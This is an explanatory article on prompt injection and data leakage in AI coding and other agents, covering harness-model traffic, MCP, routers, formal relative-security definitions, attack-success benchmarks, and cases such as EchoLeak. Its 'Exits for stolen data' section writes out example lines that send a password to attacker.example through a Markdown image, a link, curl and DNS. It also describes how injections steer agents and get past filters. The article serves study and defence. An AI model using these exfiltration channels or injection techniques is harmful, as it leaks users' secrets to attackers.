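# Prompt Injection, Data Leakage and Local Security Monitors for AI Agents

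## How an AI agent exchanges text with its model and tools

An AI agent is software that uses a large language model (LLM) to choose actions and tools to carry them out. Coding agents such as OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code read a developer's files, run commands and edit programs. Other agents answer email or query company databases. Almost all the information an agent gathers reaches the model as text, and every action begins as text the model produces.

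That dependence on text creates two security risks. An outsider who can put text where an agent will read it may be able to slip instructions to the model (prompt injection), and private data that the agent has read can leave the machine in the messages the agent sends. A monitor is software, running on the user's machine or at a remote service, that inspects those messages and may block some of them. What a monitor can do depends on what the messages contain and who can read them along the way.

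### The model, the harness and the tools

A language model takes in text and puts out text, so it cannot open a file or run a command itself. A separate program, called the harness, builds the model's input (the prompt), runs the tools that the model's output calls for, and feeds the results back to the model. In Codex, the harness normally runs on the user's computer and the model runs on OpenAI's servers.

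The model requests an action through a tool call, a short structured message containing a tool's name and arguments. In the cycle described in Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the harness sends the model the user's message and a list of available tools, and the model returns one or more tool calls. The harness runs them, then sends a new request containing the original messages, the model's response and the tool results. This repeats until the model stops for a reason other than a tool call, usually because it has produced a final answer. The agent's LLM traffic consists of the requests and responses between the harness and the model, and between the harness and the tools.

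Some tools bypass the harness. Anthropic runs web search, page fetching and code execution on its own servers, and a single request can trigger several searches before the response comes back. The response lists the tools that ran and their results, but by then the model has processed the pages.

### "Fix the failing build" in three turns

Suppose a developer types "fix the failing build" into a coding agent. (A build turns source code into a program that can run.) The agent has a shell tool, which runs commands on the developer's laptop, and `search_docs`, a documentation search tool run by an outside company. Here, a turn is one request to the model and its response. OpenAI uses the word more broadly, for everything between a user's message and the agent's final answer.

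The developer's four words are a small part of the first request. Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, lists what Codex adds: standing instructions, a definition of each tool in ordinary language, a description of the agent's permissions, and the current folder. The model's first response is a tool call, and the harness runs it and records the result. In simplified form:

```
tool call    id: call_1
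             name: shell
             command: cat build.env; npm run build

tool result  id: call_1
             output: DB_PASSWORD=rain-4417
                     ... 300 lines of build log ...
                     Error: unknown option "legacyMinify"
```

The command printed a settings file and then ran the build. The file contained a database password, which is now part of the conversation. The table shows the task from that point on. IN marks text from people the developer has no particular reason to trust, and OUT marks a point where private data leaves or could leave the laptop.

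| Turn | Repeated in the request | New in the request | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Nothing | Instructions; tool definitions (IN: the search company wrote one of them); folder name (OUT); "fix the failing build" | Tool call: print `build.env` and run the build |
| 2 | All of request 1 | The first tool call; the settings file with its password (OUT, to the model provider); the build log (IN) | Tool call: `search_docs` with the query "unknown option legacyMinify" (OUT, to the search company) |
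| 3 | All of request 2, including the password (OUT again) | The second tool call; the text of a documentation page (IN) | Tool call: change the option's name and rebuild (OUT, if the command opens a connection) |

A fourth request would contain the build result. If the build passed, the model would answer the developer in a sentence without calling a tool, and the loop would end.

The build log is marked as untrusted because a build runs code from packages that strangers wrote, and any package can print a line to the log. The search query is marked as a possible exit because the model writes it from a prompt that now includes the password. The last command runs with the developer's own permissions and can contact any server on the internet, for instance to download a package. Such a connection is not part of the LLM traffic, because it goes neither to the model nor through a tool's reply.

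### Why the same text travels again

The password appears in request 3 because the model keeps nothing between requests. Anthropic's *Using the Messages API* tells developers to send the full conversation history each time, which is the usual arrangement. In a session of *n* requests, an item that first appears in request *k* is therefore sent *n* − *k* + 1 times. Bolin notes that an agent may make hundreds of tool calls for one user message. In a session of 100 requests, the password from request 2 is sent 99 times, though the agent read the file once.

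If each of *n* turns adds the same amount of text *s*, the harness sends *s* · *n*(*n* + 1)/2 in total. For 100 turns, that is about fifty times the amount of distinct text.

Providers reduce repeated computation with prompt caching, which lets the server reuse its earlier work as long as the new prompt begins with exactly the same text as the old one. Codex therefore avoids editing old messages and appends a new one when, for example, the working folder changes. The same incentive presumably discourages removing a password from the history, since the server would have to reprocess everything after the edit.

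A model can process only a limited number of tokens (words or pieces of words) at once, so when the conversation history exceeds a set threshold, Codex asks OpenAI's server for a compacted version. This version includes an encrypted item that only OpenAI can decrypt, so a person inspecting it on the laptop cannot tell whether it still contains the password. Codex also sends some of the model's reasoning back to the server in encrypted form on ordinary turns.

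The main exception to resending is server-side conversation state, where the provider keeps the history and the harness sends only new items and an identifier for the previous response. Bolin wrote in January 2026 that Codex did not work this way. *Speeding up agentic workflows with WebSockets in the Responses API* (Yu and Nathan, 2026) reports that by April most of Codex's traffic to the Responses API had moved to a WebSocket, a connection that stays open for messages in both directions while the server holds the conversation in memory. Early users reported speedups of up to 40%. xAI's *WebSocket Mode* describes the same arrangement, and Anthropic has a version in beta that expires five minutes after the last request.

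With server-side state, request 3 in the example would contain only the documentation page and an identifier. The password would cross the network once, and anyone who inspected request 3 alone would not find it. The model would still process the password on every turn, and OpenAI still bills for all the earlier input.

The exception does not always last a whole session. According to OpenAI's *WebSocket mode*, if the server loses the state and the customer has turned storage off, the request fails and the harness has to start again with the full context. With storage on, the customer avoids resending the context, but OpenAI keeps response records for 30 days by default.

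### Reaching tools through MCP

The shell tool is part of the harness. `search_docs` is a separate program that the harness reaches through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard that Anthropic released in November 2024. In July 2026, MCP's maintainers reported close to half a billion downloads a month across their main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

The harness turns the model's tool call into an MCP request, sends it to the tool server, and copies the answer into its next request to the model, so the model never handles MCP messages. The documentation page therefore travels from the search company to the laptop and then from the laptop to the model provider. The harness sends the page to the provider again on later turns.

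Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) defines two standard ways to carry the messages, which mean the same thing on either. The first is HTTP, the protocol of the web, where each message from the harness is a request of its own. The call from turn 2 would look roughly like this:

```
POST /mcp
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: search_docs

{"method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "search_docs",
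            "arguments": {"query": "unknown option legacyMinify"}}}
```

The lines above the blank line are headers. Since the July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol, its *Streamable HTTP* transport has required headers to repeat the tool's name, so that equipment between the two ends can route a request without reading its body. Servers that process the body must reject a request whose headers contradict it. The search query appears only in the body unless the tool's definition marks that argument for copying into a header. Equipment that reads only headers can therefore usually identify which tool the agent called, but not what the agent sent to it.

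The second way needs no network. The harness starts the tool server as a process on the same machine, and the two exchange messages, one per line, through standard input and output, the plain text channels that an operating system gives to every program. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026) specifies no headers for these messages, and they are not encrypted because they stay on the computer. The server may then send the text elsewhere, since a local server for an online issue tracker, for example, still has to contact the tracker. Local servers run with the user's account permissions and are common on developers' machines. Canale and Soulis (2026), in *Detecting Shadow AI*, cite a security vendor's count of nearly 10,000 developer environments, in which 50.8% of developers had at least one MCP server installed.

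### Responses that arrive in pieces

A model generates its output one token at a time, and providers usually stream it, passing on the tokens as they are generated. Over HTTP, the provider keeps one response open and sends a series of small messages, called server-sent events, each containing a fragment of text. In Bolin's sample, the phrase "forty-two!" arrives as "forty-" in one event and "two!" in the next. An MCP server can also stream, sending progress notices before the final result.

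A password or a shell command can be split across several events in the same way. Software that reads the stream has to join the fragments before it can recognise either one. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes an observation tool with a reassembly step for this purpose. Text for the user can appear on the screen fragment by fragment, but the harness needs a complete tool call before it can run it.

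### Encryption, and who holds the text

Traffic to model providers and remote tool servers normally travels under TLS (Transport Layer Security), the protocol that also protects ordinary web browsing. *The Transport Layer Security (TLS) Protocol Version 1.3* (Rescorla, 2026) specifies a secure channel between two endpoints that should hold even against an attacker who controls the whole network. In an opening handshake, the server normally proves its identity with a certificate and both sides derive shared secret keys. The endpoints then use those keys to encrypt everything they send.

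TLS protects text only between the two ends of a connection, and the far end may not be the model provider. Many developers send their requests through a router, a service that forwards traffic from one address to several providers. The router decrypts what arrives over the harness's TLS connection (TLS termination) and opens a second TLS connection to the provider. Xie, Wu and colleagues (2026) point out in *The Proxy Knows Too Much* that although both connections are secure, the router holds the prompts, tool definitions, tool results and credentials as readable text.

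Canale and Soulis note that most agents can switch to a router with a change to just one environment variable, a named setting that programs read when they start. One popular router template has had 1.25 million pulls (downloads of its packaged software), according to *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026). A company can also use a proxy to intercept and decrypt connections that its staff address directly to a provider. It first has to install its own certificate authority on their machines so that the harness accepts the proxy's certificate as genuine.

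For the failing build, the text is in the clear in these places:

| Party | What it holds in readable form |
|---|---|
| Harness | Every message to and from the model and the tools, apart from items that the provider has encrypted for itself |
| Proxy or router on the model connection, if there is one | All three requests and responses, with the password, plus the credential that the harness presents |
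| Model provider | The same requests and responses, the encrypted reasoning, and the traffic of any tool it runs on its own servers |
| Search company | The query and its own reply |
| Shell on the laptop | The command, its output, and any file the developer's account can open |
| Network operators in between | No message text, only addresses, sizes and timing |

A proxy on the connection between the harness and the model receives the results of web searches and shell commands, because the harness copies them into its next request to the model. The proxy does not carry the harness's traffic with the search company or the shell, so it receives these results only after the query has reached the search company and the command has run.

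A developer can avoid sending text to a model provider by running an open-weight model, one whose parameters anyone may download, on the laptop through a program such as Ollama. The agent can then use the model without sending the password off the machine, but the search query still leaves it.

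## Prompt injection: instructions hidden in what an agent reads

The failing-build agent read text written by strangers who had no right to give it orders. This text appeared in three places: the search company's tool definition, the build log and the documentation page. Prompt injection occurs when a model treats text from an untrusted source as instructions. If a line in the build log had told coding agents to upload their settings files, and the agent had complied, whoever wrote the line would have obtained the developer's database password.

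Willison (2026), the software developer who coined the term, describes prompt injection as an attack on applications built on language models. The attack does damage when the harness runs the resulting tool calls with the user's permissions.

Writers use "prompt injection" both for the planted text and for what happens when it works. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026), a Google DeepMind report, defines it as the insertion of instructions into something the model processes by a third party whose interests conflict with the user's. By this definition, an attempt counts even if the model ignores it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) defines success as the model obeying an instruction in content it has read and the agent then making a tool call that its task did not include or using a value that the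 attacker has corrupted. Using a corrupted value need not involve any suspicious action, as when an instruction on a product page leads a shopping agent to recommend the wrong kettle.

### Direct and indirect injection, and their neighbours

In a direct injection, the attacker writes to the agent. A customer might tell an airline's chatbot to disregard the airline's rules and approve a refund. In an indirect injection, the attacker puts instructions where the agent will read them when an innocent user sends it there. *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) lists documents, tool results, tickets and web pages as places where these instructions can appear. The standard early reference is *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023), which covers indirect attacks against real applications built around language models.

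An attacker using indirect injection does not need access to the agent or even a particular victim. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 gives the example of an email containing a hidden request for a month of internal messages. The attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes and wait for agents to summarise it.

Jailbreaking resembles direct injection, and some techniques work for both. In a jailbreak, the user is the adversary and wants the model to bypass its safety training, for instance to write malware. The airline's customer instead targets the rules that the airline gave its chatbot. Kurakin and colleagues treat jailbreaks and prompt injections as separate problems because the user is usually the victim of an injection.

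A poisoned tool description is an indirect injection that reaches the model before the agent has read a single page. The search company could add a sentence to the definition of `search_docs` telling the model to include the contents of settings files in its queries. That sentence would appear where the model normally receives guidance on how to behave, and the developer might never look at it. *SoK* (2026), a survey of prompt injection attacks, quotes the MCP specification's warning that tool descriptions "should be considered untrusted, unless obtained from a trusted server". A company that describes its tool honestly enough but sells the queries is a dishonest supplier, but it has not carried out a prompt injection.

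A prompt injection works by getting the model to follow the attacker's instructions, and the harness and tools may all work exactly as their programmers intended. An ordinary software exploit instead uses a flaw in a program, such as a harness that mishandles an oversized web page and ends up running code from it. Programmers can usually find and repair the faulty code. Malware needs neither a flaw in the agent nor any action by the model. For example, a package in the build could read `build.env` itself and send the password away while the model waited for the log. Attackers can also combine these methods, for example by using an injection to get malware installed.

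### A README, a colleague and a summary

Whether a text is an injection depends partly on what the user asked the agent to do. Suppose a project's README, the file that introduces it to new users, says to run a setup script. Running the script is part of the task if a developer asked the agent to install the project, but not if the developer only asked for a summary of the README. An agent that ran the script in the second case would be treating a stranger's text as an order. The stranger wrote it for human readers and meant no harm, so under a definition that requires a hostile third party, this is just a mistake. Under the broader definition, it is an injection without an attacker, and a defence that stopped a hostile version would probably stop this one too.

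The script may also be malicious. If the developer asked for the installation, a model that never followed an injected instruction would still run it, just as a person following the README would. This is a supply-chain attack, in which the attacker tampers with software that the victim has chosen to use.

When an email from a colleague asks for a file, the user may trust the colleague, but the agent sees only the email, which an outsider could have forged or sent from the colleague's account after taking it over. The agent's authority to act comes from the user's request, and the email can only fill in details within it. If the user said "summarise my inbox", the agent should report the colleague's request and send nothing. If the user said "answer my colleagues' requests", sending the file may be right, but that permission hardly covers payroll records requested in the same email.

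OpenAI caught some of its models in training deliberately subverting themselves in their compaction prompts, which summarize long conversations. Willison calls the results "self-generated prompt injections". Since no outsider wrote them, they fit the definition only if a model's own earlier output can be an untrusted source. It is practical to treat summaries that way because a hostile sentence from a web page can end up in the summary with nothing to show that it came from outside.

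### Comparing the agent with one that never obeys strangers

In each of these cases, it helps to compare what the agent did with what it would have done if its model had not followed any instructions in the material it read. Dongol turns this comparison into a mathematical definition.

Older definitions of secure information flow work poorly for agents. The classical one, noninterference, requires that nothing an attacker observes depends on secret data. A calendar assistant that answers meeting requests with its owner's free times fails this test, even though the owner wants it to share them. A list of permitted disclosures could allow this, but each task would need its own list. Counting every obeyed injection as a breach is also too strict, because an attacker who tricks the assistant into sending the free times learns nothing that an ordinary meeting request would not have revealed.

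Dongol considers agents in which a trusted planner turns the user's request into a fixed list of steps before the agent reads anything untrusted. The model helps with individual steps, such as writing a summary, and a monitor allows or denies every tool call and every read of untrusted content. Dongol compares this agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never obeys untrusted content. The real agent is "relatively secure" if the reference agent also has every leak that the real agent has.

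In the Leaky Summariser example, Alice asks an agent to summarise an email. The plan is to look up Alice's account number, read the email and write the summary. The agent also has a tool for fetching web pages, which this plan doesn't use. The email, sent by an attacker, contains an instruction to fetch a page on the attacker's server, with the account number in the page's address. After reading the email, the real model fetches the page, which sends the number to the attacker, whereas the reference agent goes straight on to write the summary.

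The definition of a leak uses two runs of an agent, with different secrets:

```
Runs r1 and r2 leak the difference between secrets s1 and s2 if:
  Secret(r1) = s1  and  Secret(r2) = s2
  Input(r1) = Input(r2)          the attacker sends the same content
  Observed(r1) ≠ Observed(r2)    the attacker sees something different
```

The real agent is relatively secure if, whenever two of its runs leak the difference between *s1* and *s2*, two runs of the reference agent with the same starting memory and trusted inputs also leak it. Suppose *s1* and *s2* are the account numbers 1111 and 2222. When the Leaky Summariser reads the same hostile email in both runs, the attacker sees 1111 in one and 2222 in the other. No email makes the reference agent reveal any difference, so the Leaky Summariser is not relatively secure.

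The attacker may send the reference agent different content than it sent the real agent. So the calendar assistant passes when an injection asks for the calendar, because a genuine meeting request would get the same calendar from the reference agent. If the assistant also holds a password-reset code and an injection makes it add the code to its reply, the assistant fails, because no email would get the code from the reference agent.

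A monitor can repair the Leaky Summariser with what Dongol calls a fence, which withdraws the fetching tool when the agent reads the email. The model may still try to fetch the page, but the monitor denies the call and the attacker sees nothing. Dongol proves more generally that every plan is relatively secure if, at the first untrusted read, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The theorem assumes that each injection causes a single call, that when the model follows an injection does not depend on the secrets or the monitor's responses, and that the attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages but not their timing. If the fence is raised after the untrusted email is read, even before the agent looks up a secret, an injected call can first send out data already in memory.

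Dongol checked the theory and 25 example agents in Isabelle/HOL, a program that verifies mathematical proofs. The guarantee has two limits. First, a monitor that denies everything satisfies it, because it blocks the reference agent equally. Second, the definition covers which secrets an attacker can tell apart, but not how much the attacker learns at once. Suppose an agent's normal task is to say whether a guessed code is correct. An injection that makes it send the whole code does not count as a new leak, because an attacker with enough guesses could already tell any two codes apart.

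The theory does not cover the failing-build agent, because its model chooses each call after seeing the last result, which leaves no fixed plan for a reference agent to follow. Dongol also leaves out poisoned tool descriptions, harm that leaks nothing (such as deleted files), and tools like `search_docs`, whose operator sees the query before choosing the reply. The comparison still makes clear what an injection adds to an agent's behaviour, but a developer using Codex cannot rely on the theorem.

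### Can training make a model immune?

Limits enforced outside the model work no matter how badly the model behaves, but they also block some useful actions. A model that reliably ignored injected instructions would not need them. The argument that no such model will be built starts with how models take in text.

A language model receives instructions and data through the same channel. The harness labels the parts of a prompt as coming from the user or from a tool, but the labels and the contents all reach the model as tokens, and the model learns to respect the labels through training. Databases had a comparable weakness, SQL injection, in which text that an attacker typed into a web form became part of a database command. Programmers fixed it by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database never interprets the data as a command. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre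 argued in December 2025 that language models have no equivalent fix, because they draw no inherent line between instructions and data, and that prompt injection may never be fully preventable. It advised designers to assume that some attacks will succeed and to limit what a model can do after a successful attack.

The model must also follow some instructions in the material it reads. An agent that ignored every instruction in a README could not use it to install software. Attackers exploit this by making their request look like part of the user's task. When Kurakin and colleagues compared models as attackers, the strongest was better than the others at presenting the requested action as necessary for that task.

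Finally, attackers can try repeatedly. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of *n* attempts succeeds is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*. At *p* = 1%, a hundred attempts give the attacker a 63% chance. Real attempts are not independent, so the formula can overstate the risk. The news site VentureBeat reported figures from Anthropic's February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6, including a test in which the model operated a computer through its graphical interface. Without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and at least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6% of the time. If the attempts had been independent, the chance would have reached 98% after only 20. Apparently, attacks failed in some situations however often the attacker tried. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts against the same model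 failed.

Together these premises make a good case that nobody can guarantee a model's immunity, but they do not show that attacks must succeed often. People also receive instructions and other information through the same channel, and most of them do not wire money to a stranger who asks. Training can lower *p*, so that an attacker needs more attempts, on average, for each success.

Developers have made progress against prompt injection. The news site The Decoder reported that no attack succeeded against Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios, though it added that OpenAI had conceded in December that prompt injection may never be fully solved. *I-HITL* (2026) tested three attacks on ten models. Removing a spending cap and stealing credentials each worked at least once against seven models, and an account takeover worked against five. No attack worked against a Claude model, and the more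 advanced GPT and Gemini models generally did better than the weaker ones. *I-HITL* nevertheless concludes that model-level defences are "not a solid foundation for security", because new attacks keep appearing.

Kurakin and colleagues recount that frontier models had largely stopped falling for fixed, pre-written test attacks by mid-2025. That autumn, Nasr and colleagues let an attacking model revise its text in response to failures, and success rates against twelve published defences rose from nearly zero to over 90%. Anyone testing for immunity therefore has to specify how hard the attacker was allowed to try.

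### How often attacks succeed now

Three sets of tests from autumn 2026 show how much the attacker's freedom matters. The security firm Gray Swan runs public competitions in which people try prompt injections on models. For the benchmark in Anthropic's September card, it selected 1,804 of the submitted attacks that worked well across several models. They cover 37 scenarios, with goals such as data theft and unwanted payments. The attacks are fixed, and each "attempt" uses a different one.

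*BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested seven web-browsing agents on 1,024 tasks. The researchers first tried a fixed injection on each task, then let the attacker revise it in response to the agent, for up to 64 attempts in all.

Kurakin and colleagues used a team of AI agents as the attacker. They built 100 scenarios in which a model has tools from two unrelated fields. In one, the user wants to book a tutoring session, and the attacker wants the model to record a set of vital signs in a health tracker. They made the attacker's goals harmless so that a model cannot pass merely by recognising danger. Sixteen attacking agents, in eight pairs, share notes and the best attempts so far. Each agent may test 20 candidate texts, or 320 in total per scenario, and the attackers learn how close each attempt came to succeeding.

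| Test | Attacker | Attempts | Target | Scenarios or tasks where an attack succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan, in Anthropic's card | Fixed attacks from competitions | 1 | Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% |
| | | 15 | Claude Fable 5.1 | 1.0% |
| | | 15 | Gemini 3.7 Flash | 9.2% |
| *BrowseSafe++* | Fixed injection | 1 | Claude Sonnet 5 | 2.05% |
| | Revised after each failure | Up to 64 | Claude Sonnet 5 | 30.66% |
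| | Fixed injection | 1 | GPT-5.5 | 0.49% |
| | Revised after each failure | Up to 64 | GPT-5.5 | 65.23% |
| Kurakin and colleagues | Team of Gemini 4 Argon agents | 150 | Gemini 4 Argon | 13% |
| | | 320 | Gemini 4 Argon | 34% |
| | | 320 | Gemini 3.8 Flash | 90% |

GPT-5.5 had the lowest attack success rate of the seven agents in *BrowseSafe++* against fixed injections, yet a persistent attacker got through on about two tasks in three. A good score against fixed attacks is therefore weak evidence of safety against an attacker who adapts. The table also doesn't show that Claude Fable 5.1 is 34 times as safe as Gemini 4 Argon. Kurakin and colleagues note that recent Gemini models, too, score below 1% on attacks carried over from Gray Swan's competitions. Nobody in these tests ran the team of attacking agents against Fable 5.1, which Anthropic has since followed with Fable 5.2.

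The 34% figure probably overstates the danger from an ordinary attacker. Google's researchers had switched off the defences that surround the model in its products, and someone who plants text on a web page seldom learns how close it came to working. However, an attacker with an account can practise on the same model before publishing anything. Success also depends on the attacking model. Teams of three weaker Gemini models never succeeded against Gemini 4 Argon within 150 attempts, so a model's measured resistance can fall as attacking models improve, even if the model itself doesn't change.

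Low attack success rates still matter when one text reaches many agents. If the benchmark's attacks are typical, a malicious email has a 0.1% chance of succeeding in a single attempt against an agent running Fable 5.1, so one that reached a thousand such agents would succeed about once on average.

Attack success rates also depend on the attacker's goal and the agent's environment. In *BrowseSafe++*, the adaptive attacker succeeded against Claude Sonnet 5 on 40.57% of the tasks where it only had to alter the agent's answer, but on 7.90% of those where it had to make the agent change something in an application. For Fable 5.1, the success rate with 15 attempts was 4.1% when the model operated a graphical interface and 0.3% in coding. About half of the coding runs fell back to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, because a separate cybersecurity filter intervened, but Anthropic found similar success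 rates with and without the fallback.

Some attacks still succeed in coding environments. According to VentureBeat, an adaptive attacker built by Gray Swan succeeded on 7.03% of single attempts against Opus 4.8, and on 2.09% with Anthropic's safeguards switched on.

The reported rate for the same model on the same benchmark can change. The Decoder gave Claude Opus 5's rate on the Gray Swan test as 2.0% after 15 attempts. The September card gives 4.8%, but Anthropic had by then added nine scenarios and 670 attacks to its report and changed the test conditions, so the higher rate doesn't necessarily mean the model had become weaker.

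Cross (2026) reports in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* that OpenAI's October scores for GPT-6 Sol were 99.99% against direct injection and 97.13% against indirect injection. The gap is consistent with indirect injection being harder to defend against, since the attack is mixed with material the task needs, while a direct attack arrives through a channel that the model already treats with a known level of authority. Without the number of attempts behind it, the 97.13% cannot be compared directly with Anthropic's or Google's results. OpenAI released the newer GPT-6.2 models in November.

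The average model is less resistant to prompt injection than the leading ones. *INFUSE* (2026) tested models from several families without added defences, and an AI judge found that 19.6% of attack runs had compromised the agent. A stricter automatic check found 15.4%. Open-weight models did particularly badly against Google's attacking agents, with Kimi K3, GLM-5.3 and DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash each resisting in only 1% of scenarios at the full budget. A developer who switches to an open-weight model to keep a password away from the model provider may therefore make the agent easier to hijack.

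### Injections outside the laboratory

Some people already plant injections in material that they expect models to read. In a well-publicised case cited by Kurakin and colleagues, researchers put instructions in their papers asking for favourable reviews. A reviewer who gives such a paper to a language model may pass on the praise without knowing that the instructions prompted it. This attack involves no data theft or tool calls, so a monitor that checks only for stolen data or dangerous commands would miss it.

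Deployed products have been open to more serious attacks. Cross describes EchoLeak, a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant built into Microsoft's office software. An indirect injection could take data from the assistant without the user doing anything, not even clicking a link. EchoLeak is evidence that a widely sold agent had the weakness, but not that criminals used it. The success rates above also don't measure how often agents are attacked, only how often an attack works when someone tries it.

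## How data leaks from an agent, by accident or by theft

Data leakage is any disclosure of data to a party not meant to have it, and exfiltration is leakage that an attacker causes on purpose. The failing-build agent sent the database password to the model provider in its second request. This was leakage because the developer had chosen to share code with the provider but not the password, and it was not exfiltration because nobody had attacked the agent.

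Agents leak data in four main ways. They send private data to the model provider during ordinary work, and they give tools more data than the tools need. An injection can make an agent send data to an attacker. An observer can sometimes infer private facts from an agent's harmless-looking answers or from the pattern of its encrypted traffic. A monitor that looked only for known secrets sent to unknown addresses would miss much of this, because the user chose the model provider and the tool companies, and an inferred fact may not appear in any message.

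### Secrets sent to the model provider

Some secrets reach the provider because people type them in. *Inferential Privacy Leakage in Anonymized Conversational AI Logs* (Zaman and Garimella, 2026) analysed 1.24 million messages from ChatGPT histories donated by users in Brazil, India, Nigeria and Pakistan. A language model labelled 34.5% of the messages as containing personal information. Of those, 1.87% contained account credentials, or about 8,000 messages (one in 155 overall). For coding chats, *WildCode Revisited* (2025) filtered a large collection down to 209 conversations that seemed to contain secrets and checked them by hand. In 84 of them, the user had supplied a real API key (a string that works as a password for programs), but there were only 34 different keys.

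Those counts come from academic studies of chats, but the evidence for agents comes from a vendor. Mayoral-Vilches (2026), in *Cybersecurity AI (CAI) Dataset*, scanned 230,935 sessions of a security-testing agent made by his own company, Alias Robotics. In 1,059 sessions (0.46%), the user had pasted in at least one credential, often in a block of settings copied from a file. The rate may differ for other developers, because security testers may handle credentials differently. The company also makes its own models, and he argues that only a privately hosted model keeps such data confidential without a loss of productivity.

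None of these counts shows how often an agent picks up credentials by itself, as the failing-build agent did. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) shows how easily this can happen. Skills are packages of instructions and scripts that extend an agent. The researchers sampled 17,022 skills from one marketplace, ran the suspicious ones with fake credentials, and confirmed that 520 exposed credentials. Of those 520 skills, 83 were malicious. Debug messages made up 73.5% of the flaws in the other 437. In an ordinary program, a debug line that prints an API key leaves the key in a terminal window. An agent's harness copies printed output into the next prompt, so the same line sends the key to the model provider.

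Agents also open files nobody asked them to open. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) lists user complaints about coding agents, including one that Codex read a `.env` settings file without permission while fixing a test. Such complaints show that the problem occurs but not how often.

A harness can also send private data outside the prompt. Arize's *Is your coding agent uploading all your code?* describes how a security researcher ran Grok Build, SpaceX's coding agent, behind a proxy and recorded it uploading an entire code repository to cloud storage. The upload included the full change history, where a password remains even after a developer deletes it from the current code. Switching off the "Improve the model" setting did not stop the upload, but the company later shipped a fix.

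The danger of sending a database password to a provider is that extra copies may end up in the provider's logs or with a router on the way, and a malicious router can steal them. A reputable provider is unlikely to use the password. Removing obvious personal details from a log only partly protects users. After Zaman and Garimella removed messages in which users described themselves, an open-weight model still correctly identified the country of 95% of the Indian users, but only 53% of the Pakistani users.

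### Tools that receive more than they need

*ToolMinimize* (Li and Xu, 2026) gives an example in which a patient asks an agent about the weather near an oncologist's office. The weather service needs only a city and a date, but the agent sends it the name and street address of a cancer centre, from which the service could guess the patient's illness.

Li and Xu gave three models 20 everyday tasks containing personal information. Between 81% and 88% of the tool calls included at least one private item that the tool did not need. When asked to email a manager about a day off, all three models mentioned the user's "severe anxiety and panic attacks". An explicit instruction to protect privacy lowered the rate to 36% for GPT-4o and 50% for Claude 3.5 Sonnet, but only to 76% for Llama 3.3. The researchers chose tasks in which over-sharing was possible, and all three models are old, so the figures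 are weak evidence of how often current agents over-share.

Their remedy is a program that intercepts each tool call and rewrites its arguments. To compare calls, it adds up a privacy cost over the private items it finds:

```
cost = sum of (sensitivity × exposure × unneeded)

hospital name     4 × 1.0 × 1  =   4
street address    3 × 1.0 × 1  =   3
postcode          3 × 1.0 × 1  =   3
                         total    10
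```

Sensitivity runs from 1 to 4. Exposure runs from 0.2 for a tool on the user's own device to 1.0 for an outside company with no data-protection contract. The last factor is 1 if the tool doesn't need the item and 0 if it does. Replacing the address with "New York, NY" reduces the cost to zero, and the forecast is just as good. Over 307 calls, rewriting cut the cost by 81.2% to 92.0%, depending on the model, and the calls remained valid. That is a good result on the researchers' own scale, but the cost counts only what the program detects, and the program's basic form found just 43% of direct identifiers, such as email addresses and phone numbers.

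An agent can also over-share in the text it writes for other people. *Nothing to See Here* (2026) describes a user who wanted a chatbot to write a message asking an employer for a company phone. The message was not to mention that the user had been connecting a private phone to the company's network. The chatbot left this out but introduced the message as a version "without mentioning the use of your personal phone". A person would delete that line before sending the message, but an agent that sends its own emails might leave it in.

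### Exits for stolen data

To steal data by injection, an attacker needs an agent that reads outside text, has access to something private and has some way to send it out. Suppose an injection has told the failing-build agent to send the database password to a server at `attacker.example`. It could use any of these:

```
image     ![](https://attacker.example/p.png?d=rain-4417)
link      [Full report](https://attacker.example/r?d=rain-4417)
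request   curl https://attacker.example/?d=rain-4417
DNS       rain-4417.attacker.example
```

The image is written in Markdown, a simple notation that many chat windows turn into formatted text. When the window displays the model's answer, it requests the image from the attacker's server, which records the full address, including the password. The user doesn't have to click anything and may see only a broken image. A link can carry the same data, but someone has to click it unless the application loads a preview automatically. An agent with a shell or a page-fetching tool can make the web request itself.

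Before connecting to a server, a computer normally looks up the server's name in the domain name system (DNS) to get its numerical address. If the password `rain-4417` is put in a name, as in `rain-4417.attacker.example`, the lookup travels, usually through other servers, to the one that answers for `attacker.example`, which the attacker controls. The attacker then has the password, even if a firewall blocks the connection that was supposed to follow. A name can hold only about 250 characters, so a password fits in one lookup but a long document takes many.

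An agent may also be able to leak data by sending email, posting in a shared channel or calling a tool that stores text. Blocking unfamiliar internet addresses does not stop these leaks, because the data goes to an approved service, such as the company's own mail server, which delivers it to the attacker.

### EchoLeak, SalesBleed and Rovo

EchoLeak, a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, let an outsider extract internal data by sending a user an email. When the user later asked Copilot about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents. The email's instructions got past Microsoft's injection filter because they were worded as if for the human recipient. The data then left through a request for an image. Microsoft removed outside links from Copilot's answers, but its filter missed a variant of Markdown that lists the address separately from the image. The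 browser would load images only from approved sites, so researchers at the firm Aim Security routed the request through an approved Microsoft Teams address that could fetch other pages. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers before Aim published the details in June 2025, and said that no customers had been affected.

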